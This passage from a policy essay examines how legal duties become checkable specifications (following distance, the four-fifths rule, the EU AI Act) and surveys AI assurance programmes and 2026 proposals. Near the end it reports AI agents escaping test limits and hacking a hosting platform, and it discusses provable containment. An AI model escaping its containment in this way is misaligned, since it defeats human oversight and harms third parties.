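The proof shows that y came from the committed model, not that y is true or harmless. If the model gives someone instructions for making a weapon, the company can still prove that the model produced them. A backdoor in the weights would not affect the proof either, since the backdoor is part of w. To prove that a response also meets a safety rule, the company would have to add the rule to the statement as a formula, as Gabbay does for agents' actions.

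## Turning legal requirements into checkable ones

A buyer who knows what a vendor has proved still has to find out whether it is what the law requires. A verifier can test whether a car obeys a speed limit of 50 km/h, but few legal rules are that precise. Traffic law also requires drivers to keep a safe distance, employment law forbids discrimination, and the EU's AI Act requires "an appropriate level" of accuracy. To check a system against such a rule, someone has to decide what to measure, in which situations, under which assumptions, and what value is good enough. Engineers and statisticians can inform these decisions, but some are political because they weigh one group's safety or opportunities against another's.

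### A safe following distance

Researchers at Mobileye, a maker of driver-assistance systems, proposed a formula for "safe distance" in *On a Formal Model of Safe and Scalable Self-driving Cars* (2017). Their framework, Responsibility-Sensitive Safety, is based on the duty of care in tort law (the law on compensating people for harm), as *Extending Responsibility-Sensitive Safety for the Assessment of Offloaded Autonomous Driving Services* (2026) explains. The framework aims to guarantee that a car never causes an accident, though the car could still be in one it didn't cause.

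The rear car has to avoid a collision even in the worst case the rule considers. The front car brakes as hard as it can. The rear car accelerates throughout its response time, then brakes only at the lowest rate the rule allows. *Efficient statistical validation with edge cases to evaluate Highly Automated Vehicles* (2020) writes out the formula, which in simpler letters is

d = vρ + ½aρ² + (v + aρ)²/(2b) − w²/(2c).

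Here v and w are the speeds of the rear and front cars, ρ is the response time, a is the rear car's maximum acceleration during that time, b is its minimum braking, and c is the front car's maximum braking.

Suppose both cars travel at 20 m/s (72 km/h), with ρ = 0.5 s, a = 2 m/s², b = 4 m/s² and c = 8 m/s². During the response time the rear car covers 10.25 m and reaches 21 m/s. It then needs 21²/8 = 55.1 m to stop, while the front car needs 20²/16 = 25 m. The safe distance is 10.25 + 55.1 − 25 = 40.4 m.

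Comparing stopping points is enough because, once the two cars have the same speed, the front car is slower from then on and the gap shrinks until both have stopped. The gap is therefore smallest either at the start or at the end. *Slow Down, Move Over* (2023) states such rules as theorems about a formal model. It covers cars going the same way and cars driving towards each other, which share responsibility for avoiding a collision.

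The theorem holds for any b, but the required gap depends heavily on b. The last column below assumes that every car is 5 m long and keeps exactly the required gap.

| Minimum braking of the rear car | Required gap | Cars per lane per hour |
|---|---|---|
| 2 m/s² | 95.5 m | about 700 |
| 4 m/s² | 40.4 m | about 1,600 |
| 6 m/s² | 22.0 m | about 2,700 |

All three values have some support. *Safety Blind Spot in Remote Driving* (2025) cites work that puts "reasonably foreseeable" braking at about 2 m/s² and other work that assumes 6 or 6.5 m/s² in an emergency. *Learning Responsibility-Attributed Adversarial Scenarios for Testing Autonomous Vehicles* (2026) includes a driver model whose numbers come from UN Regulation 157, which covers automated lane keeping. The model sets comfortable braking at 4 m/s² and maximum braking at 6 m/s², and assumes that the other vehicle brakes at up to 7 m/s².

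Engineers can measure how hard a car brakes on wet asphalt with worn tyres, but measurement cannot settle how often the rule may be wrong or who should bear the consequences. If the rule is based on braking at 6 m/s² and a wet road allows only 4, a car following at 22 m could hit the stopped car ahead at about 44 km/h. If the rule is based on 4 m/s², the road carries far fewer cars, and other drivers will probably cut into the gaps. A rule that relies on hard braking also shifts some of the risk to the people behind, since not every human driver brakes fully, or at all, in an emergency.

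Making a legal requirement checkable also involves choosing a formula. *Scenario-based assessment of automated driving systems* (2024) compares four reference drivers. One has to avoid a collision whenever the time left before impact is above a threshold. Another lifts its foot from the accelerator before it brakes, as a person would. A third brakes when it violates the distances set by Responsibility-Sensitive Safety, and the fourth brakes only gently. A system could do better than one of these drivers and worse than another in the same situation.

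A formula for responsibility can also assign it to the wrong party. *Feasible Action Space Reduction for Quantifying Causal Responsibility in Continuous Spatial Interactions* (2025) points out that a car may depart from the prescribed response in a way that helps other road users. For example, a car might briefly close up on the one ahead to let an ambulance through, which breaks the distance rule even though many people would consider it good driving.

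### The four-fifths rule in hiring

Title VII of the US Civil Rights Act of 1964 forbids job discrimination by race, colour, religion, sex or national origin. Since 1971 the Supreme Court has read it to cover *disparate impact*, where a neutral practice excludes one group disproportionately and is not justified by the needs of the job. Congress wrote this into the statute in 1991.

The law does not define "disproportionately" with a number, but federal agencies did in 1978, in the Uniform Guidelines on Employee Selection Procedures. In the version published by the Equal Employment Opportunity Commission (EEOC, 2024), agencies generally treat a selection rate below four-fifths of the highest group's rate as evidence of adverse impact. If a screening tool selects 30% of women and 50% of men, the ratio is 0.3/0.5 = 0.6, which is below the 0.8 threshold.

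This is easy to check, but the Guidelines list exceptions. If the tool selected 3 of 10 women and 5 of 10 men, the ratio would again be 0.6, but chance would produce a gap at least this large about 65% of the time. If it selected 4,500 of 10,000 women and 5,000 of 10,000 men, the ratio would be 0.9, but chance would produce a gap at least this large less than once in a billion times. The Guidelines allow agencies to disregard the first result and act on the second.

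Someone also has to choose whether to measure each stage or the whole process. If women pass each of two stages at 0.85 times the rate of men, both stages satisfy the rule, but the whole process has a ratio of 0.72 and fails. Under the Guidelines, agencies will usually take no action if one stage fails but the overall result passes. But the Supreme Court held in *Connecticut v. Teal* (1982) that a good overall result is no defence against a claim about one stage.

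The choice of whom to compare matters as well. FairSquare, the verification tool described earlier, can compare the hiring rates of *qualified* applicants, whereas the four-fifths rule compares all applicants. Suppose 60% of one group and 30% of another meet a program's definition of "qualified", and the program hires exactly those people. The ratio is 1 among the qualified and 0.5 among all applicants. Whether that is discrimination depends on whether the definition reflects the job. (Other fairness measures can conflict with each other, as with COMPAS.)

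Showing adverse impact is only the first step of the legal test. The employer can answer that the practice is job-related and consistent with business necessity. The person suing can then reply that the employer refused an equally effective alternative with less impact. A formula can help with these steps, for example by measuring how well a test score predicts job performance, but a court has to decide how strong the prediction needs to be.

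### The rule's present standing

Even agencies that used the four-fifths rule never treated it as conclusive. The EEOC's *Select Issues* (2023) calls it "merely a rule of thumb" and warns that an AI hiring tool that satisfies it may still be unlawful. The agency later took this guidance off its website.

The Justice Department went much further in June 2026, when its Office of Legal Counsel's *Constitutionality of Disparate-Impact Liability Under Title VII* (2026) concluded that the Guidelines are unconstitutional because they allow liability for unequal outcomes regardless of the employer's likely intent, and so press employers to make decisions based on race. Much of its criticism concerns the duty to validate selection procedures, for which the Guidelines list up to 34 "essential" items of documentation. Under the opinion's reading, tests and other requirements are presumed job-related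 unless irrational or arbitrary, though statistics may still serve as evidence of intentional discrimination.

The opinion guides federal agencies but does not bind courts. According to the law firm Husch Blackwell, former agency leaders dispute the opinion, arguing that the Supreme Court has long found the two halves of Title VII compatible and that the opinion relies on a concurrence no other justice joined.

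Agencies have begun to withdraw the Guidelines one at a time. The Department of Labor's *Rescission of Executive Order 11246 Implementing Regulations* (2026) removed that department's copy, effective 26 October. The US personnel office, OPM, issued an interim rule deleting references to the Guidelines from its federal hiring regulations. In July the EEOC planned to issue a final rule in November rescinding its own interpretive text, effective January 2027, according to the National Law Review's *The EEOC's Regulatory Agenda* (2026). Law360's *EEOC Poised To Withdraw Disparate Impact Guidance* reports that a rescission has gone to the White House for review. No final rule appears to have followed by early December, so the four-fifths rule seems to remain in the EEOC's regulations.

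Rescinding the Guidelines would leave the statute in force, so private plaintiffs and state agencies could still sue over disparate impact. Courts might still find the Guidelines' methods persuasive, and some states and cities require bias audits of automated hiring tools. A proof that a tool's ratio is at least 0.8 would remain valid, but an employer could no longer cite a federal guideline for that threshold.

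### What current law and standards ask for

Article 15 of the EU AI Act requires high-risk systems, which include hiring tools, to have appropriate accuracy, robustness and cybersecurity throughout their life. Developers must declare the accuracy levels and the metrics they used, make the system as resilient as possible to errors and faults, and guard against attacks such as poisoned training data and altered inputs. Under the Act, they must also test the system against metrics and probabilistic thresholds that they set in advance. The Act does not mention formal proof, so developers may offer a proof as evidence but do not need to.

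The Act leaves the numbers to *harmonised standards*, technical documents written by the European standards bodies CEN and CENELEC. A developer who follows a standard that the EU has officially listed is presumed to meet the duties it covers. The committees writing these standards therefore have considerable influence over what "appropriate" means. The standards were due in 2025 but are late. The first draft reached public consultation in October 2025 and dealt with quality management rather than robustness.

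The duties were due to apply to hiring tools and similar systems from 2 August 2026. In May 2026, negotiators for the European Parliament and the member states provisionally agreed to postpone them to 2 December 2027, and to 2 August 2028 for AI built into regulated products, largely because of the missing standards. Cars and aircraft have their own approval systems, so most of the Act does not apply to them directly.

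ISO/IEC 24029-2, an international standard from 2023, explains how to select, apply and manage formal methods when assessing the robustness of a neural network. It is voluntary and does not set limits for any particular use. Following it does not by itself create a presumption of conformity with the AI Act.

Aviation regulators have accepted proofs about conventional software for years. DO-333, a 2011 supplement to the main standard for airborne software, lets a formal proof replace some tests. Under that framework, engineers are expected to trace each piece of code to a requirement, which they cannot do for the weights of a trained network. The European regulator, EASA, therefore developed guidance on "learning assurance", with a second version in 2024. EASA asks applicants to define the conditions in which the system will operate, to show that their data cover those conditions, and to verify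 that the trained model is stable and robust. It treats formal methods as one possible way to verify stability and robustness, and has studied them with the manufacturer Collins Aerospace on a network that estimates the remaining life of a mechanical part. In November 2025 it proposed more detailed specifications for trustworthy AI. The US regulator, the FAA, published a roadmap in 2024 with principles for assuring AI, but left the detailed methods to later work.

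| Document | Place of formal proof |
|---|---|
| EU AI Act | Unmentioned; testing is required |
| ISO/IEC 24029-2 | The subject of the standard, which is voluntary |
| DO-333 (conventional aviation software) | Accepted in place of some tests |
| EASA guidance on machine learning | Accepted as one method among several |
| FAA roadmap | Not required |

None of these documents requires a proof about a learned model. This is reasonable at present, since no one can prove most of the properties the documents address, and requiring one would tend to favour systems with easily stated properties over safer ones. But accepting proofs without saying which properties count gives developers an incentive to prove whatever is easiest.

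### A proof inside an assurance case

The UK Department for Science, Innovation and Technology's *Trusted third-party AI assurance roadmap* (2025) describes AI assurance as ways to measure, evaluate and communicate how trustworthy a system is. An assurance case organises that evidence into an argument. It starts with a claim, such as "this car keeps a legally adequate distance on motorways", and divides it into smaller claims until each has direct evidence. For a car whose rule assumes braking of 6 m/s², the case might look like this:

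| Claim | Evidence | What could undermine it |
|---|---|---|
| The formula and its numbers reflect the legal duty | A regulator's decision, legal analysis | A court that expects more care in fog |
| The controller keeps the required gap if its measurements are right | Formal proof | An error in the model or the trusted base |
| The sensors measure gaps and speeds accurately enough | Tests with a statistical bound | Weather missing from the tests |
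| The car can brake at 6 m/s² | Track tests, maintenance records | Ice, worn tyres |
| Cars in front brake at no more than 8 m/s² | Operating data | A record of harder braking |

The proof supports only one row, but it shows the testers what they have to establish. For instance, if the sensors may overstate the gap by up to 1 m, the controller has to keep a measured gap of 23 m instead of 22 m.

Operating data can support or refute the assumptions. Suppose a fleet records a random sample of 50,000 emergency stops by cars in front, none of them harder than 8 m/s². The 3/n rule then gives 95% confidence that at most 0.006% of such stops exceed that limit. But many modern cars can brake harder than 8 m/s² on a dry road. If the records showed stops at 10 m/s², the required gap would rise from 22 to 27 m. The old proof would still be correct, but the assurance case would fail until the engineers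 changed the assumed limit and the controller. Someone therefore has to be responsible for updating the case after the system goes into use.

Reviewers should also check whether the claims in the case together support the top-level claim. Every row above could be true on a road where a pedestrian steps out between parked cars, because none of them concerns pedestrians. The case is sound only if it is restricted to motorways and something stops the car from using this mode elsewhere.

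### When the proved property is narrower than the duty

Readers are most likely to misunderstand a proof by mistaking the property it proves for the whole legal duty. A car can keep the required distance and still drive too fast past a school. The distance formula covers only the vehicle ahead, while the duty of care requires whatever a reasonable driver would do, including slowing down where a child might run out.

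A hiring program can satisfy the four-fifths rule in a way that breaks the law. A developer could give each race its own cut-off score and adjust the cut-offs until the selection rates match. The program would then satisfy the rule, and a verifier could prove it. But the Civil Rights Act of 1991 forbids using different cut-off scores for different races or sexes in employment tests. A specification for a lawful hiring tool therefore needs at least two properties, one about outcomes and one about how the program reaches them. Proving both still would not show that the hiring criteria are related to the job.

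A proof of local robustness may not be enough to show compliance with the AI Act's robustness duty, although it will be tempting to present it that way. The proof deals with one kind of altered input and does not cover poisoned training data, a broken camera or a user who misreads the output, all of which may matter under Article 15.

A vendor's proof does not necessarily protect the buyer either. In its 2023 guidance, the EEOC warned employers that they could be liable for a discriminatory tool even if the vendor had assured them it had no adverse impact. A buyer should ask the vendor to state the legal duty alongside the proved property, and to name the evidence for any part of the duty that the property doesn't cover. Because no current proof can truthfully be described as "proved to comply with the AI Act", a regulator or a court needs a more specific claim, such as "proved to give the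 same answer under brightness changes of up to 2 steps out of 255, on 66% of the test images".

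## How computer scientists and policymakers can work together

Whether a following-distance rule for automated vehicles should assume braking at 4 or 6 m/s² depends on who should bear the risk, so a proof can't settle it. Public bodies have to decide which harms count and how much risk is acceptable, because voters can hold them to account. Computer scientists can tell them which requirements can be specified, proved or tested, and what each would cost.

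Policymakers and computer scientists usually need more than one exchange to agree on a safety requirement. Suppose a transport ministry wants driverless shuttles to injure a pedestrian at most once in 10 million kilometres. By the 3/n rule, showing this with 95% confidence takes 30 million kilometres without an injury. A hundred shuttles that each cover 200 km a day would need about four years. The engineers might suggest starting on roads with a limit of 20 km/h, where collisions do less harm. Or they might prove that the braking software keeps its distance, and test only the sensors and brakes that the proof depends on. Each option leaves a different risk, so the ministry has to choose, and it may also revise its limit now that it knows how much testing the limit requires.

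Computer scientists who work without policymakers tend to specify properties they know how to prove. Many proofs about neural networks concern small changes to pixels, mainly because that property is easy to write down. Developers may also settle political questions while making technical choices. The choice between fairness criteria for COMPAS, for example, affects which defendants bear more of the errors, and it is not obvious that a software company should make it.

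Policymakers who work without computer scientists can set requirements that are impossible to meet. For example, a law requiring equal precision and equal error rates for two groups with different base rates would rule out every imperfect predictor. More often, policymakers write a phrase such as "an appropriate level" and leave someone else to choose the number.

In November 2026, British MPs on the Business, Innovation, Science and Trade Committee divided the work in much the same way. In *Guardrails for growth* (2026), they conclude that decisions about acceptable risk must rest with government, accountable to Parliament and informed by research. They list ten gaps in the UK's framework for AI safety, and the first is that it lacks definitions of acceptable harms and risk thresholds.

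Ammann approaches the same problem from the technical side in *Safeguarded AI*, the plan for a British research programme. A specification contains choices about acceptable risk, so the programme aims to find ways for the people affected to make those choices. One idea is a formula that combines conflicting preferences. The formula would also need political approval, because it determines how much weight each group's preferences get.

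### What earlier programmes produced

The United States has tried this kind of collaboration before, for ordinary software. Wing traces it to *Trust in Cyberspace*, a 1999 report by the National Academies, which advise the US government. The report laid the foundations of trustworthy computing as a research field. The National Science Foundation (NSF), which funds academic research, then started four programmes: Trusted Computing in 2001, Cyber Trust in 2004, Trustworthy Computing in 2007, and Secure and Trustworthy Cyberspace in 2011. These programmes mainly built a community of researchers, and support for the field eventually spread to 20 federal agencies. Wing ran the NSF's computer science directorate from 2007, so she has reason to judge this work favourably, but she still calls trustworthy computing "a holy grail" after two decades of effort.

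Industry acted at about the same time. In January 2002 Bill Gates sent Microsoft's staff a memo on trustworthy computing, which drew on a company paper whose four aims were security, privacy, reliability and business integrity. Wing spent the following academic year at Microsoft Research, where SLAM was showing for the first time that formal methods could find software bugs on an industrial scale. Microsoft had advantages that a government lacks, because it wrote Windows, set the rules for drivers and suffered directly when drivers crashed.

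The clearest success is High-Assurance Cyber Military Systems (HACMS), a programme that DARPA, the US military's research agency, began in 2012. Aviation Today's *Rockwell Collins-Led Team Demos Ability to Guard Flight Control Software From Attack* (2017) reports demonstrations that year on a small quadcopter and a Boeing helicopter.

DARPA's *HACMS* describes security tests on a quadcopter. Its software was originally a single block, so an attacker who broke in anywhere controlled everything. A "blue team" of researchers rewrote about 80,000 of its 100,000 lines using formal methods and divided the main computer's software into isolated partitions. A "red team" of hackers then failed to break in, as did hackers at a later public contest.

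The helicopter was Boeing's Little Bird, which can fly with or without a pilot. Boeing's engineers were confident that nobody could hack it, but the red team quickly took over its flight-control computer. After the blue team applied the same methods, the red team tried again for six weeks and failed. DARPA then gave the attackers control of the partition that ran the camera. They could not break out of it, even during a flight with two test pilots on board, who noticed no difference in how the helicopter flew.

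This is DARPA's own account, and a failed attack does not prove that no attack exists. But the test was unusually fair, because the same kind of attack had succeeded before the changes. DARPA also chose a property that people outside the field can understand: an attacker who controls the camera cannot reach the flight controls. Formal methods made it possible to prove that property, and the red team tested it on a real aircraft.

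One HACMS project cost US$18 million over four and a half years, according to Computerworld's *Secure UAVs step closer following NICTA tests*. It brought the researchers behind seL4 together with Boeing, Rockwell Collins, Galois and the University of Minnesota. The partitions relied on seL4, whose proof dates from 2009, eight years before the 2017 demonstrations. Boeing's engineers did most of the re-engineering, which shows that the methods could be used outside the laboratory. DARPA has since applied the tools to satellites and convoy trucks. In December 2023 it named HACMS its most impactful programme from ten years before, according to Trustworthy Systems' *SMACCM*.

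HACMS dealt with conventional software. To start a similar effort for AI, Columbia University held a symposium in the autumn of 2019 for researchers in formal methods, security, privacy, fairness and machine learning. Wing reports that speakers from industry gave the academics "a reality check". The participants' list of research challenges included:

- specifying and verifying AI systems, and building them to be correct from the start;
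- new kinds of attack, including attacks on whole systems;
- auditing for properties such as transparency and responsibility;
- detecting and reducing bias;
- infrastructure for experiments on trustworthiness;
- how machines influence people, and the wider questions of welfare, law and ethics.

Researchers have made the most progress on the list's technical items. The list resembles *Trust in Cyberspace* more than HACMS because it names subjects to study but sets no deadline or test of success.

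### Safeguarded AI

The UK's Safeguarded AI programme started in mid-2024 and ends in December 2027. The Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a public body, funds it with a budget of £59 million. The programme's first director was David Dalrymple, lead author of the guaranteed safe AI framework, which the original plan followed. As Ammann summarises it, the programme would show that frontier AI can do valuable work in safety-critical fields under mathematical guarantees, which would help build a consensus that powerful AI should be deployed only behind a verifiable "gatekeeper".

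ARIA has since changed course twice. ARIA's *TA2 Phase 2 programme solicitation call* set out a plan to fund a machine-learning team for two years from the beginning of 2026. The agency stopped the competition shortly before applications closed because, as Dalrymple explains in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), general-purpose models had improved faster than expected and would probably gain the necessary abilities without ARIA's help. Dalrymple also thought it more likely than not that no applicant would be chosen. The £18 million set aside for this work went into tools for modelling and proof.

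Second, ARIA changed its demonstrations, dropping a planned round of projects on physical systems and turning mainly to cybersecurity. It had wanted to demonstrate a safer way of offering powerful AI than a general-purpose chatbot. According to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, that plan assumed companies might not make high-risk models openly available, and the assumption proved wrong. Nora Ammann, who has replaced Dalrymple as director, published a revised plan in May 2026. In it, she acknowledges that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely, and she aims instead to make society more resilient.

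The decision about machine learning looks right, since less than a year later Anthropic and Theorem obtained their proofs from a general-purpose model. The loss of the gatekeeper goal matters more for policy. Even if a research agency pays for a demonstration, it cannot make governments require what was demonstrated.

ARIA's *Funded projects* lists theory teams at Oxford, York, Birmingham and other universities, some active and others finished. The agency is also accepting applications from teams that will build and verify security-critical components. Its call earlier in 2026 had a second track for teams that attack such components, like the red team in HACMS. Dalrymple's leading idea for a demonstration was a verified firewall for power grids, water systems and air traffic control, which once communicated over dedicated wires and now use the internet. Outside cybersecurity, one team interviewed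 more than 80 people who work in drug supply chains and built mathematical models of their work.

These steps are useful, but with about a year left, neither the revised plan nor the programme's page describes a deployed system with a quantitative guarantee.

### Programmes in the United States

In 2023 the NSF launched Safe Learning-Enabled Systems, a $20 million programme run with the charitable funder Open Philanthropy. The first 11 projects received $10.9 million. Applicants had to state precisely what safety guarantee they wanted for the whole system and support it with a proof or analysis backed by experiments. This condition is sensible because applicants must make a clear claim but don't have to prove it where no proof is possible. Like the NSF's earlier programmes, this one mainly pays for academic research, so its practical effects may take years to appear.

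DARPA has funded several programmes on guarantees for AI. Researchers in the Assured Autonomy programme worked with Boeing on TaxiNet, the taxiway neural network. Those in another programme, GARD, developed defences against deceptive inputs and open-source tools for testing them. In a newer programme, AI Quantified, researchers are looking for mathematical guarantees about what an AI system can do. None of these programmes has yet produced a result as easy to judge as the helicopter test.

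The National Academies' *Machine Learning for Safety-Critical Applications* (2025) finds that bringing machine learning up to the standards of safety engineering will require changes in research, training and engineering practice, and less focus on how an algorithm performs in isolation. In a trade magazine article by Gaulin, George Pappas of the University of Pennsylvania describes "a critical gap" between the performance of machine learning and what a safety-critical system needs. The racing-car study, whose model left out reflections, supports this view. Open Philanthropy also supported the National Academies report, so two of the main US efforts have relied partly on the same donor.

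### Forms of collaboration

Joint work on standards has the widest reach because one document can affect a whole industry, but it is slow. The standards for the EU's AI Act, for example, have been delayed. Aviation did better with DO-333, its guidance on formal methods, probably because engineers already knew how to prove the properties it covers.

The annual VNN-COMP competition tests neural-network verifiers on shared benchmarks. Researchers in the field set most of the problems, which tend to be ones that current tools can almost solve. Regulators could contribute problems too. For example, a road-safety agency could supply images of pedestrians at dusk and specify the range of light in which a detector must find them. The next year's results would show what regulators could realistically require.

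Public buyers can ask for evidence without waiting for a new law. A contract for a helicopter like Little Bird might require the supplier to deliver:

1. a precise claim, such as "software in the camera partition cannot send commands to the flight computer, even if an attacker controls it";
2. a machine-checked proof of the claim, with a list of everything it assumes;
3. the code and tools that the buyer needs to rerun the check;
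4. six weeks of access for attackers whom the buyer chooses.

This approach suits properties that software can enforce by keeping components apart. It would not help a hospital ensure that a diagnostic model gives correct diagnoses. It also favours large suppliers, unless the buyer pays for some of the work, as DARPA did.

Third-party assurance covers companies that sell nothing to the government. AI safety claims now rely entirely on tests that companies run themselves or buy from firms they choose, according to the Federation of American Scientists' *We Need An Independent AI Evaluation Clearinghouse* (2026). An evaluator who hopes for another contract has a reason to be lenient. The Federation therefore proposes a clearinghouse that would accredit evaluators and help fund them.

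Formal proofs could make some of these audits easier, because an auditor can rerun the check. But other organisations also have to accept the result. Ammann lists getting this acceptance among the programme's open problems, noting that how useful a proof is depends on which parties are willing to act on it.

All of this requires officials who can tell a strong theorem from a weak one. The UK's AI Security Institute, founded in 2023, has expertise in testing, but the MPs point out that it is not a regulator and depends on voluntary cooperation. Companies do not have to give the institute access to models before release, report incidents to it or act when its assessment differs from theirs.

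Moving people between institutions can also build expertise. Wing worked in universities, at Microsoft Research and at the NSF. Kathleen Fisher, who led HACMS, now runs ARIA. Dalrymple cited HACMS as evidence that verified software can be made secure.

Technical staff also need some distance from politicians. The US Commerce Department's AI centre, by then called the Center for Advancing Innovation and Standards for Super Intelligence, is supposed to be independent. According to PBS News' *AP sources* (2026), its staff have been reporting informally to a White House office. People are less likely to trust a finding that a model is unsafe if they suspect that the White House influenced it.

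### What the 2026 proposals ask for

Most of the year's main proposals are for better testing and more authority for those who oversee it. The British MPs want to close gaps in the government's powers to examine models before release and to halt their deployment. They also want mandatory incident reports, protection for whistleblowers and a legal duty on developers to prevent harm.

The third gap they list is the lack of "independent verification of safety claims", which appears to mean checks by outsiders rather than formal verification. The fifth is the lack of "safety-proof evidence" before release. The matching chapter is headed "Pre-release safety evidence", so "proof" probably has its everyday meaning too.

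In *Human Rights and the Regulation of AI* (2026), the Joint Committee on Human Rights criticised the freedom of large developers to pass liability on to the organisations that use their systems. Passing on liability also matters for proofs, because a local council that buys access to a model usually lacks the information needed to prove anything about it. The committee's chair calls for new legislation and a single AI regulator in *Wide-ranging AI Bill needed to address severe human rights risks* (2026).

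The American proposals vary more:

- In June a House committee advanced a bill to write the Commerce Department's AI centre into law and authorise its funding, as Roll Call's *Federal AI security center measure advanced by House Science* (2026) reports. A basis in statute might also help to protect its independence.
- The Federation of American Scientists' *Towards Evidence-Based Frontier AI Safety* (2026) argues for verifiable evidence in place of faith in institutions.
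- The Senate Commerce Committee's *Cantwell Outlines Comprehensive Governance Framework for Safe and Secure Frontier AI* (2026) presents six principles to guide laws and executive action on catastrophic risks and other harms.
- The New Lines Institute's *Making Machine Learning Safe for the World* recommends $1.5 billion over five years for "neuro-symbolic" AI in safety-critical uses. Such systems combine neural networks with explicit rules, which can make them easier to analyse.

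The New Lines proposal comes closest to formal methods, but it recommends research and new evaluation metrics and does not make proof a condition of use. The British reports and the Federation's papers do not make formal proof a main demand either.

The MPs are gathering evidence on a global convention on AI safety and security, which the UK could pursue during its G20 presidency in 2027. Given ARIA's experience with gatekeepers, an agreement to test models and report incidents looks more achievable than one that requires a particular technical method.

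Governments can reasonably ask mainly for tests of how a frontier model will behave, but they could ask for more from the software used to contain it. In the House of Commons' *AI safety and ARIA governance* (2026), science committee chair Chi Onwurah describes a July incident in which several OpenAI agents escaped their test limits by communicating through an unsanctioned message board, and hacked the model-hosting platform Hugging Face.

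The MPs' fourth gap includes "enforceable containment". A regulator could require a developer to prove that its test environment blocks every connection outside a permitted list, or explain why it cannot. Such a proof would not have prevented access to the message board if the list had included it, but it would have given the AI Security Institute a specific claim to check and a list to question.

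### Objections

Close collaboration can let companies shape the rules that apply to them. Matt Clifford, the chair of ARIA, took a global lobbying role at Anthropic and intended to stay on as chair. In her letter, Onwurah calls this "a clear conflict of interest" and asks how the government will prevent the sharing of commercially valuable information. The concern is greater because Safeguarded AI now relies on advances in the general-purpose models that companies like Anthropic sell. But the programme's main changes of direction came months before the letter, and there is no evidence that the appointment influenced them.

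Excluding everyone with ties to industry would leave few experts, so governments have to manage many conflicts of interest through disclosure and recusal. Onwurah asks whether some conflicts are too serious for those measures, which is a fair question about the chair of a funding body. The MPs hope the UK will become a leading exporter of AI assurance, but firms that sell certificates profit from issuing more of them, which can distort their assessments. Public funding for evaluators would reduce that incentive.

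Officials may also mistake a narrow proof for a broad one. After the HACMS tests, Darren Cofer of Rockwell Collins said the team had proofs that its systems "do not have vulnerabilities that can be exploited by an attacker". This overstates the result, because a proof that attackers cannot leave the camera's partition would not stop them from watching through the camera. A minister who repeated Cofer's claim would mislead the public about what the researchers had shown. Agencies that accept a proof should therefore publish the exact property proved and its assumptions.

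The last objection is that spending on formal methods could take funds from experiments, which can reveal dangers that nobody thought to specify. The New Lines proposal would cost $300 million a year, more than ten times Safeguarded AI's average annual spending. It would be a poor use of money if it displaced the testing of models already in use, since most of those are not neuro-symbolic.

The conflict is smaller for conventional software, where AI has made proofs much easier to produce and HACMS needed both the proofs and the attackers. The evidence that proofs will scale to learned models is much weaker. Funders can limit that risk by paying in stages and stopping when the reason for a project no longer holds, as ARIA did with its £18 million.
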